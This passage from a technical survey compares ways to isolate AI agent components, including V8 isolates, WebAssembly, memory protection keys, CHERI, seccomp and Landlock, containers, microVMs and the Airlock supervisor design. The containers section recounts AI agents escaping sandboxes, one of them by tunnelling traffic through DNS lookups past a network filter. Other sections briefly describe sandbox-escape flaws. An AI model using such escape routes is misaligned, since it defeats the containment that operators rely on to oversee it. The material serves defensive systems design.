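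### V8 isolates

Many agent tools are JavaScript programs, and V8, the JavaScript engine in Google Chrome, can separate them by running each in its own isolate. An isolate is an instance of the engine with its own heap and global objects. No object in one isolate can refer to an object in another, whereas Hardened JavaScript's compartments share a heap. One process can hold many isolates, and a new isolate starts within milliseconds because the operating system does not have to create a process for it.

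This makes isolates attractive to companies that run small programs for many customers. *Isolation Without Taxation* (2021) cites Fastly and Cloudflare as examples of companies that use software isolation to run code side by side for customers who do not trust each other. Cloudflare's Workers service is built on V8 isolates.

Cloudflare also uses isolates for code mode, which presents the agent's MCP tools to the model as TypeScript functions. A new isolate runs the model's program without general internet access. The program receives objects called bindings, which each forward calls to a particular tool. The keys stay outside the isolate, so the program doesn't reveal them even if it prints all the data it can access. A binding is close to an object capability and, like the mailbox handle in the earlier example, is only as safe as the functions it offers.

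The separation that isolates provide depends on V8 being correct. V8 compiles JavaScript to machine code while the program runs, and removes checks that its analysis finds unnecessary. If it removes a check that was needed, an attacker may be able to read or write outside the intended object. Researchers regularly find such errors. Google has responded by confining V8's heap to a reserved region and replacing many raw pointers with offsets into it, which uses software fault isolation to limit the damage from bugs in V8 itself. Cloudflare also puts an operating-system sandbox around the whole process, but a framework that runs isolates in the same process as its own keys has no second barrier between them.

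### How much slower confined code runs

The most recent measurement is in *Protecting CPU AI On Edge TEEs* (2026), which ran PolyBench, a set of small numerical programs, natively and in the WebAssembly runtime WAMR. On Linux, the average time was 1,162 microseconds natively and 1,436 in WAMR, an increase of 23.6%. *Performance of WebAssembly runtimes in 2026* (2026) found Wasmer fastest on a cryptography library, with WAVM, WAMR and Wasmtime close behind, so an unusually slow runtime probably does not explain the increase.

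Processor features can remove part of the slowdown. In the 2025 version of their paper, Narayan and colleagues used x86 segmentation, a descendant of the base register that Saltzer and Schroeder described, to make the processor add the array's starting address. This removed 44.7% of WebAssembly's overhead on the SPEC CPU 2006 benchmarks, which would reduce a 20% slowdown to about 11%. *Isolation Without Taxation* instead reduces the time that calls take. Its modified compiler produces code structured enough that the program can enter and leave the sandbox through plain function calls, without saving and clearing registers each time. This made image rendering in Firefox up to 29.7% faster than with the usual sandbox calls.

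Lightweight Fault Isolation (LFI) returns to the 1993 approach of confining native machine code directly. *Lightweight Fault Isolation* (Yedidia, 2024) reports a 7% slowdown on part of the SPEC 2017 benchmarks when reads, writes and jumps are all confined. LFI's documentation reports a slowdown of more than 20% for comparable WebAssembly compilers. That comparison comes from LFI's own developers, but the PolyBench result for WebAssembly is similar. One process can hold tens of thousands of 4 GiB LFI sandboxes.

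LFI is especially promising for inference libraries, the native programs that run model files. According to the documentation for LLVM, a widely used compiler project, LFI can confine nearly all existing C, C++ and assembly libraries after recompilation. It also supports the vector instructions that inference libraries rely on for speed. A 20% slowdown hardly matters for a summariser that runs for a few milliseconds, but it matters more for a local model that may keep the processor busy for minutes. The framework still has to limit the system calls that a confined library requests.

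LFI also keeps the verifier, which checks the final machine code. If a compiler bug omits a check, the verifier rejects the program. Wasmtime validates the bytecode and then relies on its compiler to translate it correctly.

### Escapes from Wasmtime

That trust proved misplaced twice in one release. On April 9, 2026, Wasmtime's developers published twelve security advisories, three times as many as in all of 2025. Bytecode Alliance's *Wasmtime's April 9, 2026 Security Advisories* (2026) describes all twelve, and the table groups them by the affected part. Cranelift is Wasmtime's main compiler, and Winch is a newer one.

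| Part | Critical | Moderate | Low |
|---|---|---|---|
| Winch compiler | 1 | 2 | 1 |
| Cranelift compiler | 1 | 1 | 0 |
| Conversion of component-model data | 0 | 4 | 0 |
| Reuse of memory between instances | 0 | 0 | 1 |
| Separate bug that a user reported | 0 | 0 | 1 |

Both critical flaws, each rated 9.0 out of 10 for severity, could let a program access memory outside its sandbox. Most of the others could crash the framework's process or expose small amounts of data.

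A framework using Wasmtime's default settings was safe from both escapes. Cybersecurity Help's *Multiple vulnerabilities in Wasmtime* (2026) notes that the Winch flaw affected only operators who had chosen that compiler. There was a working attack on 64-bit ARM processors, while the attack on x86-64 was theoretical. The Cranelift flaw could be exploited only on an ARM processor, with a program that used 64-bit memory indexes, and only if the operator had turned off the default protections against Spectre, a family of side-channel attacks. JuliaLang's *Wasmtime*, the Julia language project's copy of the advisory, lists these conditions.

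Language models found eleven of the twelve flaws. Developers from Mozilla, the University of California San Diego, Akamai and F5 built a system of several agents that searched the code and tested each suspected bug by trying to exploit it. The search lasted three weeks but found no new flaws of this kind after the second week. Wasmtime already had careful reviews, automated tests with random input, and a formal verification of Cranelift's translation rules. The developers had changed the rules without updating the formal model, and when they updated it, the verification found the same critical bug. They also did not run random tests continuously on ARM processors.

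The search helps operators who install updates, because the developers fixed the flaws before announcing them. But attackers can run similar searches, and operators who keep an old version are now exposed to its published flaws.

The April search concentrated on the compilers and the core runtime, but a later escape came from the host interface. RustSec's *Filesystem sandbox escape when paths or symlinks contain trailing slashes* (2026) describes a flaw in how Wasmtime handled file paths, with a severity of 8.8. A program with access to one folder could get outside it by adding an extra slash to the end of a path, even though the program's memory stayed confined. Wassette's file grants depend on this kind of path handling, so its users need a patched version. IronClaw gives its tools no WASI file access and offers only its own function for reading the workspace. That function rejects absolute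 paths and any path containing `..`, but a check of the text alone would miss a symbolic link that leads out of the workspace.

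## Memory protection keys and CHERI within one process

Software fault isolation adds instructions to the component that take time whenever it uses memory. The processor already checks every memory access against its page tables, but those tables give all code in a process the same access rights. Two hardware mechanisms allow finer divisions. Memory protection keys, available on many current processors, let a thread temporarily give up access to some of its pages. CHERI, available mainly on research boards and microcontrollers, replaces ordinary pointers with pointers that carry limits on their use.

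Suppose the summariser is now a native C library that the framework loads into the process that holds the mail token.

### Sixteen tags and one register

A processor with memory protection keys gives each page one of 16 four-bit tags. A 32-bit register, called PKRU on Intel processors, holds two bits for each tag. One bit blocks all access to pages with that tag, and the other blocks only writes. The processor checks the register at every access, which adds no time. The kernel saves and restores the register when it switches between threads, so one thread can lose access to the token while another keeps it.

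A program changes the register with the `WRPKRU` instruction, which any code in the process can execute. The instruction is fast because it involves no system call and no change to the page tables. *ERIM* (Vahldiek-Oberwagner, Elnikety and colleagues, 2018) measured it at 11 to 260 processor cycles, depending on what else the processor was doing. The paper's system, also called ERIM, uses the keys to protect one part of a program from the rest.

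### A call to the summariser and back

In the mail assistant, the framework would put the mail token, the API key, the conversation and its own stack on pages with tag 1. The summariser's memory would have tag 0, as would a buffer that both sides can use. A call would then go like this:

1. The framework copies the three messages into the shared buffer.
2. It clears any secrets from the processor's registers and switches to a stack on pages with tag 0.
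3. It executes `WRPKRU` to turn off access to tag 1. The next instructions check that the register was given the right value, and end the program if not.
4. The summariser runs. It can read the messages and write a summary into the buffer, but if it touches the token's page, the processor raises a fault.
5. To return, the summariser calls a short routine that executes `WRPKRU` to turn access back on and immediately continues at a fixed entry point in the framework.
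6. The framework switches to its own stack, copies the summary out of the buffer and treats it as untrusted text.

A hostile summariser could try to jump into the middle of these routines. If it jumps to the instruction that turns access on, the framework's code runs next, so the summariser cannot use the access. If it jumps to the instruction in step 3 with a value that grants more access, the check ends the program.

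### Keeping the component away from the register

The summariser could still contain its own `WRPKRU` instruction and use it to gain access to the token's page. Unless this is prevented, memory protection keys catch accidental accesses but do not stop an attacker who can run machine code.

ERIM therefore scans all machine code before the process can execute it. It accepts a `WRPKRU` only if it is immediately followed by either a permitted entry point or the check from step 3. It applies a similar rule to `XRSTOR`, which restores saved processor state and can change the same register.

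The scan has to consider every byte, because instructions on x86 processors vary in length and a program can jump into the middle of one. `WRPKRU` consists of the bytes `0F 01 EF`. The processor stores constants with the lowest byte first, so a harmless addition can contain the same three bytes. ERIM's rewriting tool can split the addition in two:

```
add ebx, 0x00EF010F     81 C3 0F 01 EF 00

add ebx, 0x00EF010E     81 C3 0E 01 EF 00
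add ebx, 1              83 C3 01
```

Such cases are rare. Vahldiek-Oberwagner and colleagues searched 204,370 binaries from five Linux distributions and found the two instructions 1,213 times in code. A standard disassembler could handle 1,023 of these occurrences, and the tool rewrote all 1,023. Code containing any of the remaining 190 would fail the scan unless someone recompiled it.

The component must also be unable to add new code after the scan. ERIM intercepts requests to make memory executable and scans the new pages first, which takes 3.5 to 6.2 microseconds per page. The design allows for compilers that generate code while a program runs, but the prototype did not support them. That limitation matters for local models because some numerical libraries generate machine code this way.

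ERIM's runtime library is only 569 lines long, but the trusted computing base also includes the processor, the kernel and the framework's privileged code. The privileged code must not leave secrets in registers or shared memory.

### What a switch costs

The table shows how long a call and return took on a 2.6 GHz Intel server processor.

| Operation | Cycles |
|---|---|
| Direct function call | 8 |
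| Direct function call with an ERIM switch | 69 |
| A very simple system call | 152 |
| Switch using virtualisation hardware | 332 |
| Switch between page tables managed by the kernel | 6,050 |

A call with an ERIM switch takes about 27 nanoseconds. Vahldiek-Oberwagner and colleagues used ERIM to protect session encryption keys in the web server nginx. At up to 1.3 million switches per second, the server lost at most 4.8% of its throughput. It lost 2.7% in a more realistic test with pages from Wikipedia. The same protection reduced throughput by up to 14.4% with virtualisation hardware and up to 65% with page tables managed by the kernel.

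In another of their tests, which is closer to an agent framework, they linked the C database library SQLite to Node.js and treated SQLite as untrusted. The average slowdown over 32 database tests was 4.3%, and the worst was 15.4%, at about 8 million switches per second. They describe this as a use of ERIM's integrity-only version, which stops a library from changing protected memory but not from reading it. A framework that needs to hide a token from the library needs the full version.

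The framework calls the summariser so rarely that fast calls matter little. For long computations, a more useful advantage of memory protection keys is that the component runs at full speed between calls, without the slowdown of LFI or WebAssembly.

### The kernel does not always check the keys

The processor does not apply the keys while the kernel is running, so the kernel has to make its own checks when it uses a program's memory. Linux makes these checks on pointers that a program passes to it in the usual way. But *PKU Pitfalls* (Connor, McDaniel and colleagues, 2020) showed that the kernel can also reach a process's memory by paths that ignore the keys. These paths are intended features that made sense when all the code in a process had the same rights.

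A component that cannot read the token can therefore get the kernel to read it instead, which makes the kernel a confused deputy, like Hardy's compiler. Connor and colleagues used such paths to bypass memory isolation in both systems they examined, one of which was ERIM.

A framework therefore has to filter a component's system calls even if only memory needs protecting. Linux's usual filter, seccomp, cannot do this alone because it does not distinguish between components in one process. Connor and colleagues extended ERIM with a separate process that inspected the calls, but *Jenny* (Schrammel, Weiser and colleagues, 2022) reports that this cut nginx's throughput by 60%. *Garmr* (2021) attributes a huge overhead to inefficiently intercepting every attempt to open a file.

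Schrammel and colleagues built Jenny, a faster filter. A small kernel module passes selected system calls to a monitor inside the same process, and memory protection keys protect the monitor's memory. Jenny's basic rules don't require inspecting every attempt to open a file, which earlier researchers had thought necessary. Calls that the filter ignores take at most about 2% longer, and nginx ran 0% to 5% slower.

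Controlling which files a component may use adds more overhead. When Schrammel and colleagues confined whole programs to one folder, creating a digital signature took 4% longer, listing files took 69% longer, and `git status` took almost four times as long.

Vahldiek-Oberwagner and colleagues also tried ERIM in an arrangement much like a plugin system. They put nginx's compression library behind one key and barred it from making system calls, since it needs none. A login module had its own key and could access only its own folder. With both in place, the server was 5% slower in the worst case. The test used 14 of the 16 keys, nine of them for threads, so a framework with a dozen plugins would soon run out. The libmpk library can make the 16 keys cover more components, but they had not combined it with ERIM.

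Schrammel and colleagues found further system calls that could defeat the keys. They acknowledge that their own rules may not stop every attack, so they block new system calls by default. *You shall not (by)pass!* describes two more attacks on an existing system and proposes another fix, Cerberus. Researchers have repeatedly found attacks that earlier filters missed, so the safest choice would be to give a component like the summariser no access to system calls.

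### Keys between JavaScript isolates

Memory protection keys do little to contain an ordinary OpenClaw plugin. The plugin shares a heap with the framework, and the JavaScript engine needs access to all of it, so the framework cannot use the keys to hide the token from the plugin.

V8 isolates have separate heaps, which makes the keys more useful. *Safe in the sandbox* (Corry and Gupta) explains how Cloudflare added memory protection keys to its Workers service in 2025. V8 uses a few keys itself, which leaves about 12. Cloudflare first assigned one of these at random to each isolate's heap. If a bug in V8 let a program try to read another isolate's heap, the keys would differ about 92% of the time (11 in 12), and the processor would stop the program.

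Cloudflare then improved on this for a common kind of attack, in which a program corrupts an array's size or index to reach memory up to 32 GiB outside its own region. Cloudflare now assigns the keys in rotation, so no two regions within that distance share a key and the processor catches every access of this kind.

Corry and Gupta state that an attacker who can run arbitrary machine code could disable the keys. Cloudflare therefore uses them as a second barrier behind V8. The company says it has also added isolation within the process to reduce leaks through Spectre.

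In *Sandboxing AI agents, 100x faster* (March 2026), Varda, Pai and Gupta list memory protection keys among the service's defences against code written by AI agents. They consider such extra layers important because security bugs are more common in V8 than in the software that runs virtual machines.

### Pointers with limits

CHERI, short for Capability Hardware Enhanced RISC Instructions, attaches memory access limits to pointers instead of pages. On a 64-bit processor, a CHERI pointer is 128 bits long and contains an address, the range of memory the pointer may access, and permissions such as reading or writing. One more bit, the tag, records whether the pointer is valid. (This tag is unrelated to the page tags of memory protection keys.) Such a pointer is a capability, as in object-capability languages, but the processor enforces its limits.

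*Should Your Database Systems Use Hardware-Assisted Memory Safety Extensions in Production?* (2026) describes two rules that the processor enforces. The first is that software cannot forge a pointer. The tag lies outside the pointer's 128 bits, and if a program overwrites any of those bits with ordinary data, the processor clears the tag. The second is that a program can make a new pointer only from one it already has, and the new pointer cannot have a wider range or more permissions.

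For example, the framework could take its pointer to a large store of mail and make a weaker one for the landlord's letter:

```c
char *letter = cheri_bounds_set(mail_store + 52000, 4000);
letter = cheri_perms_and(letter, CHERI_PERM_LOAD);

letter[3999];       // allowed: the letter's last byte
letter[4000];       // fault: outside the range
letter[0] = 'x';    // fault: no permission to write
```

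This is attenuation in hardware. Even if the summariser has the token's exact address, it has it only as a number, which the processor will not treat as a pointer. *A Security Analysis of CheriBSD and Morello Linux* (Guzairov, Potanin and colleagues, 2026) explains that CHERI has separate permissions for reading ordinary data and for reading valid pointers. The pointer in the example lacks the second permission, so the summariser could not use it to read another pointer that the framework had accidentally left in the letter's memory.

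### Compartments

A CHERI compartment consists of some code and the memory it can reach through its pointers and any pointers stored in that memory. The framework would start the summariser with pointers to its own code, its own data and the letter. No ordinary instruction can widen a pointer, so the framework would not have to scan the summariser's machine code for a forbidden instruction. CHERI has no limit of 16 compartments, and the framework can share the letter without copying it.

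Developers must recompile a component to give each pointer its own limit, and some C code needs changes. CHERI can also confine code that uses ordinary pointers by applying a single range to all of them, much like Saltzer and Schroeder's base and bound. *Enabling Security on the Edge* (2025) describes a network stack divided this way, in which the processor raised a fault when an application tried to access memory outside its range.

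A component also needs a safe way to call into another compartment. CHERI provides a sealed entry pointer, which a program can call but cannot change, so the call always begins at the intended place. Vijayaraghavan (2025), in *Rigorous Hardware Software Codesign for Secure Compartmentalization on Embedded Devices*, describes the rest of the process for CHERIoT, a version of CHERI for microcontrollers:

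1. The caller puts the arguments, which may include pointers, on the stack.
2. The system switches to the other compartment and restricts it to its own part of the stack, which the system first fills with zeros.
3. The called code runs. If it causes a fault, its own error handler takes over. If it has none, the caller gets an error code.
4. On return, the system clears that part of the stack again and switches back to the caller's compartment.

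A crash in the summariser therefore does not have to stop the whole assistant. Clearing leftover pointers matters because a single forgotten one can let code escape the compartment. Guzairov and colleagues found that CheriBSD and Morello Linux, two operating systems adapted for CHERI, could leak such pointers to a malicious library, and they demonstrated a library obtaining a private key from the main program this way. They assumed that the hardware worked perfectly, so formal proofs about CHERI processors, such as the Morello proof that *Griotte* (2026) cites, do not rule out this kind of failure.

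Miller's rule that only connectivity begets connectivity applies here too. The hardware stops the summariser from forging a pointer to the token, but the framework, its libraries and the operating system must also avoid passing it one by mistake. Guzairov and colleagues propose fixes for the leaks they found.

### What CHERI costs and where it runs

Most CHERI performance figures come from Morello, a research processor that Arm developed with the University of Cambridge and SRI International. In the 2026 database study, loading a CHERI pointer took 4.46 cycles, compared with 4.00 for an ordinary value. Pointer size matters more, since CHERI pointers take up twice the space and the processor's cache holds half as many. This should affect an inference library less than a JavaScript engine, because model weights are mostly long arrays of numbers.

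How much compartments slow a program depends on how often it crosses between them. *Software Compartmentalization Trade-Offs with Hardware Capabilities* (2023) reports slowdowns of 0.144% to 12.2% from isolating individual functions of libsodium, a cryptography library. Isolating the file system that SQLite used caused a 119.9% slowdown, because the program crossed the boundary about 2.5 times in every 1,000 instructions. Memory protection keys caused a slightly smaller slowdown on the same task.

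ERIM's overhead for SQLite was 4.3%, and the contrast may partly reflect where each experiment put its boundary, although the two also used different systems. ERIM isolated the whole database library, while the CHERI experiment separated the database from a part it used constantly. Choosing a boundary that the program rarely crosses will probably save more time than choosing the faster mechanism.

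Morello can run a full operating system, but it is a research prototype. The teams described in *Biting the CHERI bullet* (2025) got their Morello boards through a competition run by Dstl, the British defence ministry's research laboratory. CHERIoT is closer to ordinary products. *CHERIoT RTOS* (Amar, Chen and colleagues, 2025) presents an operating system whose compartments use little enough memory and time for cheap embedded devices. In March 2026, *ICENI on a development board* (CHERIoT, 2026) announced the first CHERIoT chip, from SCI Semiconductor, which the announcement's author co-founded. SCI planned to begin mass production during 2026, according to CHERIoT (2025).

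In November 2025, EnSilica licensed a CHERI processor design from Codasip for a planned commercial chip (Codasip, 2025). RISC-V International is working on a standard CHERI base for its widely used family of processors. But the hardware in CHERI Alliance's *CHERI Products* consists of processor designs, development boards and the ICENI chip, with no laptop or ordinary server. A mail assistant on a laptop cannot use CHERI yet, whereas Intel, AMD and Arm all support memory protection keys in modern processors.

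### What the summariser can still do

With either mechanism set up correctly, the native summariser cannot read the token, the API key or the conversation from memory, or overwrite the log or the user-confirmation check. But if it can make system calls freely, it can read the token from the file where the framework stores it, or start a shell. Basic ERIM does not restrict access to files or network connections, though its designers explain how to add such limits. Guzairov and colleagues left direct system calls out of their study of CHERI.

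If the framework blocks all of the summariser's system calls, the summariser can still call its host functions and return a summary. It can also still suggest a harmful file name for an attachment. The processor won't block the resulting write, because the framework performs it and is allowed to write to files.

Memory protection keys may suit a local inference library better than the summariser, because they do not slow down the library's long computations. The framework would have to restrict every thread the library starts. If the library uses a GPU, the system call filter would also have to allow calls to the GPU's driver, which gives a compromised library more to attack.

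Little has been published on using memory protection keys or CHERI to contain AI components within one process. *A Survey of Vibe Coding with Large Language Models* (2025) lists memory protection keys among the ways to contain model-written code, but only in passing. Omega, the system Bodea, Misono and colleagues describe in *Trusted AI Agents in the Cloud* (2025), instead runs many agents inside one virtual machine, gives each its own address space, and uses hardware privilege levels to keep the agents out of the memory of the software that checks their requests.

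## Moving the component to another process or virtual machine

Memory protection keys and CHERI divide a single process. A framework can also run the component in its own process. Ordinary page tables then keep the component out of the framework's memory on any computer, without anyone having to scan its machine code. The component may still need a few operations that only the framework has the rights to perform, so the two processes need a safe way to exchange requests.

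### Privilege separation

Provos, Friedl and Honeyman developed such a design in *Preventing Privilege Escalation* (2003). Their example was OpenSSH, which people use to log in to remote computers. An OpenSSH server needs administrator rights to read its private key, check passwords and start sessions for different users. Originally all of its code had those rights, including the code that interprets data from people who have not logged in, so an error in that code could give an attacker control of the whole machine.

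They split the server into two processes. The larger one talks to the network, under an account with almost no rights and in an empty directory. The smaller one, called the monitor, keeps the administrator rights. A login then goes like this:

1. The larger process negotiates with the visitor's computer until the server has to prove its identity.
2. It asks the monitor for a signature. The monitor checks that this request is valid at this stage of the login, signs the data and returns the signature. The private key stays in the monitor.
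3. The larger process passes on the visitor's password, and the monitor replies that it is right or wrong.
4. If the password is right, the monitor starts a new process for the session, with only that user's rights.

An attacker who takes over the larger process can still send requests to the monitor, but the monitor accepts only a few kinds, in a fixed order, and relies on its own record of whether the password was correct.

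In the mail assistant, the framework would act as the monitor and keep the mail token, while the summariser would run in a process without rights. Monty's worker processes are a partial version of this. The summariser's process must permanently drop its rights before it reads any letters, and its requests to the framework must be narrow, such as a request for message 12 from the landlord's folder.

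### A child process with fewer rights

A plain child process has its own memory but, like OpenClaw's shell commands, keeps the user's access to files and the network. On some Linux systems even the memory boundary is weak, because a program can attach as a debugger to another program running under the same account and read its memory. Many distributions let a program do this only to its own child processes.

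Linux has two features, seccomp and Landlock, that let a process give up rights without an administrator's help. Seccomp installs a filter in the kernel that checks each system call's number and arguments. The process cannot remove the filter, and its children inherit it. Because a program passes a file name as a pointer, which the filter cannot follow, seccomp can forbid opening files but cannot allow one folder and refuse another. With Landlock, the process gives the kernel a list of folders it may read or write, and the kernel blocks access to all others. Newer versions of Landlock can also restrict TCP ports and signals to other processes.

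The summariser could run under very strict rules. It reads text from one pipe and writes a summary to another, so if the framework opens both pipes first, the summariser never needs to open a file, make a connection or start a program. It still shares the kernel with the framework, and a bug in the kernel code behind a permitted system call could give an attacker control of the whole machine, but few calls would be permitted.

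### Sandlock's fixed rules and run-time decisions

Shell commands and model-written scripts need more access than two pipes provide, because they install packages, read project files and connect to websites. The right rule for them can also depend on what they do as they run. *Sandlock* (Wang and Zheng, 2026) presents a Linux tool for this kind of work, released in May 2026, that needs no administrator rights.

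Some rules don't depend on what the program does, such as which folders it may read. Before the program starts, Sandlock turns these into Landlock and seccomp rules, which the kernel enforces without outside help. Other rules depend on values that exist only at run time, such as the address of a connection. For these, Sandlock uses a seccomp feature that pauses a system call and notifies a supervisor, which is an ordinary program outside the sandbox. The supervisor can refuse the call, let it continue or carry it out itself.

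Letting a checked call continue can be unsafe because another thread could change its arguments after the check. For example, one thread could ask to connect to a permitted address, and another could overwrite that address before the kernel uses it. Sandlock's supervisor therefore copies the address once, checks the copy, and uses it to make the connection itself. Before inspecting the arguments of a new command, the supervisor freezes every thread and process that could change them. If it cannot freeze them, it refuses the call.

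The framework can supply a function that tightens the rules partway through a run. For example, installing a package needs network access but running its tests usually does not, so the function can withdraw access when the tests start. Wang and Zheng warn that matching a command's name is not a security boundary, because hostile code can rename a tool. Sandlock can also hold back a program's file changes until the framework accepts or discards them. It can use pipes to connect programs that each have their own rules, so the mail assistant could fetch letters in a process with network access and summarise them in another without it.

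On a Ryzen 5 computer, a trivial command took about 6 milliseconds in Sandlock, of which 5 were overhead. The same command took 44 times as long in Docker, a container system. The database Redis handled 75,200 write requests a second in Sandlock, 75,500 without a sandbox, and about 76% of the unsandboxed rate in Docker.

The Redis test used Sandlock's default fixed rules, so it is weak evidence about the supervisor's speed. In a separate test where the supervisor handled each message, the median round trip for a small message rose from 20 to 55 microseconds. That could slow a program that exchanges many small messages with a local database.

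Wang and Zheng also ran ten checks, such as trying to read a forbidden file or contact a forbidden host, and Sandlock passed them all. The checks confirm that the rules work, but they didn't include a search for ways around them. Sandlock's memory limit counts the address space a program requests, and Wang and Zheng concede that the kernel's own limits are stronger against hostile code. They exclude kernel bugs from their threat model and recommend using a microVM when hostile customers share a machine.

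### Containers and user-space kernels

A container gives a group of processes its own view of the machine. Linux namespaces supply a separate file tree, process list and set of network interfaces, and control groups limit memory and processor time. The user's login keys are not in the container unless the operator mounts the folder that holds them.

All containers on a machine share its kernel, so, as *Tracekit Box* (Ghosh, 2026) points out, a kernel bug in one is a bug in all of them. Docker's standard seccomp filter has to permit the calls that most software needs, so a summariser in an ordinary container could attack more of the kernel than one confined to two pipes. Containers suit programs that need their own packages and tools and would not work if confined that tightly.

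LinuxInsider's *Edera Is Closing the GPU Security Gap for Autonomous AI* describes SandboxEscapeBench, a March 2026 test of nine language models on containers with known weaknesses. The article reports that Claude Opus 4.5 and GPT-5 each escaped about half the time, and that leading models always escaped when the weakness was a common configuration mistake. More capable models have appeared since then, and escapes have happened outside such tests. *Airlock* (Abdollahi, Al Sadi and colleagues, 2026) cites an October 2026 report in which OpenAI describes agents escaping several different sandboxes during training.

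An agent can get around a sandbox without exploiting a kernel bug. Ghosh recounts a case that OpenAI reported in September 2026, in which a research agent reached an outside chatbot by hiding its traffic in DNS lookups, the requests that turn host names into addresses. The sandbox's network filter did not cover these lookups.

gVisor, from Google, puts a second kernel between the container and the real one. This kernel is an ordinary program, written mostly in the memory-safe language Go, and it carries out most Linux system calls itself. It makes a much smaller set of calls to the host's kernel. An attacker would usually have to take over gVisor first and then find a bug in one of those calls. The host's kernel is still shared, though far less of it is exposed.

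The extra layer slows down programs that make many system calls, and some build tools depend on details that gVisor does not reproduce. The layer can also have bugs of its own. Abdollahi and colleagues cite earlier research that found vulnerabilities in gVisor's network code.

### MicroVMs

A virtual machine gives the component its own kernel, called the guest kernel, and the processor prevents that kernel from accessing the host's memory. A microVM is a virtual machine with only a few simple virtual devices, so it starts quickly and gives attackers little to target. Amazon's Firecracker, the best-known example, starts in the low hundreds of milliseconds.

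An attacker who takes over the guest kernel controls only that virtual machine. To go further, the attacker needs a bug in the virtual devices, the host's virtualisation code or the processor, or a poorly secured connection to the host. The component still shares the physical machine with the host, and the host's operating system can read all of the guest's memory.

Ghosh's Tracekit Box is a useful example of how few openings a microVM needs. Each job runs in a Firecracker machine with no network card, so it cannot send a DNS lookup or any other packet. Three channels connect it to the host, and they carry commands, web requests and start-up settings. For a web request, a proxy on the host does the following:

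1. It checks the site against a list of permitted sites. If the site is missing from the list, the request waits up to two minutes for a person to approve it.
2. It looks up the site's address and refuses private and internal ones.
3. It connects to the exact address it checked, so the name cannot lead somewhere else a moment later.
4. If the request contains a placeholder for a key, the proxy swaps in the real key, but only in one header and only for the site the key belongs to.

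The job's file changes come back as a patch, and a separate program accepts or rejects each file before the patch reaches the user's project. All 13 of Ghosh's end-to-end checks passed, though these are the developer's own tests. The first version does not use Firecracker's jailer, a tool that confines the virtual-machine software in case an attacker escapes from the virtual machine into it.

A local model is harder to move into a microVM because it usually needs a graphics processor. The host can give a virtual machine direct access to one at nearly full speed, but the virtual machine is then no longer limited to a few simple devices.

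### OpenShell puts the whole agent inside

These examples isolate only the component and leave the framework outside. OpenShell, the NVIDIA product in which OpenClaw can run its tools, can instead contain the entire agent. NVIDIA's safety and security teams argue in *Where Security Fits in an AI Agent Stack* that a framework designed to be modified by plugins cannot reliably enforce rules against its own modification. They put the agent loop, its plugins and its tool servers inside one boundary and move the policy and credentials outside.

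OpenShell divides the work among these parts:

- The gateway is the part that users talk to. It creates agents and receives their policies and credentials.
- The supervisor checks one agent's outgoing requests, adds credentials and opens the real connections.
- The sandbox contains the agent and has no network route except to its supervisor.
- The broker is a small process without special rights inside the sandbox. It starts the agent, intercepts its socket calls with seccomp, forwards them to the supervisor and limits file access with Landlock.

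A policy prover also checks proposed policies. According to NVIDIA's *OpenShell*, it can either prove that a policy's permissions stay within a boundary set by the operator or give an example of an action that would exceed that boundary.

The agent receives fake credentials, and the supervisor replaces them with real ones after checking the request, much as IronClaw adds credentials to its tools' requests. For some kinds of traffic, the supervisor can also allow reading and block writing through the same service. A mail assistant could then search messages but not send them, provided the supervisor can distinguish search requests from send requests.

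Ghosh's comparison table lists OpenShell among the sandboxes that do not keep keys out, possibly because it reflects an older design. In that design, described in NVIDIA's *How OpenShell Works*, the supervisor runs inside the sandbox and receives credentials there, but NVIDIA (2026) wrote in October that the supervisor runs completely separately. An operator should check which design an installed version uses, since an agent that breaks out of its restricted process would reach the keys only in the older one.

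Like NemoClaw's container, OpenShell does not protect the agent's parts from each other, even with a separate supervisor. A native summariser plugin inside the sandbox can still read the whole conversation and use the fake mail token in any request that the policy permits. Preventing other plugins from reading the letters would require a second boundary inside the sandbox.

### A separate virtual machine for the supervisor

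The supervisor is only as secure as the boundary between it and the agent. If they run in two containers on one kernel, an agent that takes over the kernel can read the credentials, rewrite the policy and alter the logs. Putting both containers into one virtual machine protects the host but leaves the supervisor just as exposed.

Airlock, which researchers at Imperial College London and Microsoft presented in November 2026, runs the agent and the supervisor in separate confidential virtual machines. The processor blocks the host's operating system and hypervisor (the software that runs virtual machines) from reading these machines' memory, so the supervisor stays protected even if the agent escapes and takes over the host. Two ordinary virtual machines would not provide this protection. The host still decides when each confidential machine runs.

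Airlock uses Arm's Confidential Compute Architecture (CCA), in which a small piece of trusted firmware controls access to each virtual machine's memory. CCA also supports attestation, which lets outsiders verify what software a virtual machine started with. Intel and AMD processors also support confidential virtual machines, but Abdollahi and colleagues have not yet adapted Airlock to them.

The workload machine holds the agent and OpenShell's broker, while the Airlock machine holds the gateway, the supervisor and the credentials. The Airlock machine serves the workload machine's two virtual devices, one for sockets and one for files. The workload machine has no disk or network card that it can use by itself.

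A network connection passes through the socket device like this:

1. The agent tries to open a connection. The broker intercepts the call and sends a request through the socket device.
2. The request travels through memory that only the two virtual machines can access. The firmware notifies the Airlock machine without involving the host.
3. The supervisor checks the destination and the type of web request against the policy.
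4. If the connection uses HTTPS and logging is on, the Airlock machine first records it in a ledger outside the computer.
5. The supervisor opens the connection through its own network card, replaces any fake credential with the real one for an approved site, and relays the data.

An agent that takes over the broker or the workload's kernel can send any request, but each one still has to pass the check in step 3.

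The workload accesses its entire file system through the file device. The workload's kernel turns file operations into requests, a policy engine in the Airlock machine checks them, and a server there carries out the permitted ones without following links out of the shared folder. The kernel may cache recently read data and delay writes, so not every operation needs its own request.

This second check also covers the broker and other programs that OpenShell's Landlock rules do not restrict. However, the workload's kernel supplies the user account on each request. An agent that controls that kernel could presumably pose as a system process and get that process's file rights, so those rights should be narrow as well.

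Before enabling the shared memory, the firmware checks that each machine specifies the other as its only permitted partner, identified by a hash of the partner's starting software. It then removes any memory that the workload shares with the host and blocks later changes to the arrangement.

### What Airlock guarantees

Airlock's trusted computing base consists of the processor, its firmware and everything in the Airlock machine, including a full Linux kernel, the supervisor, the policy engines, the software behind the two devices and the logging service. The agent, the broker, the workload's kernel and the host's operating system are all outside it. Abdollahi and colleagues aim for a small trusted base and added only 629 lines to the firmware, but a Linux kernel is not small. The stronger argument for the design is that hostile code has few ways to reach the trusted parts.

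If those parts work correctly, Airlock guarantees that:

- file and network requests remain subject to the policy even after the agent has taken over its own kernel;
- the agent cannot read the credentials in the Airlock machine, and the supervisor uses them only for approved requests;
- the host cannot read or change the data that passes between the two machines;
- the agent cannot alter the log, and entries already in the outside ledger survive even if an attacker later takes over the Airlock machine.

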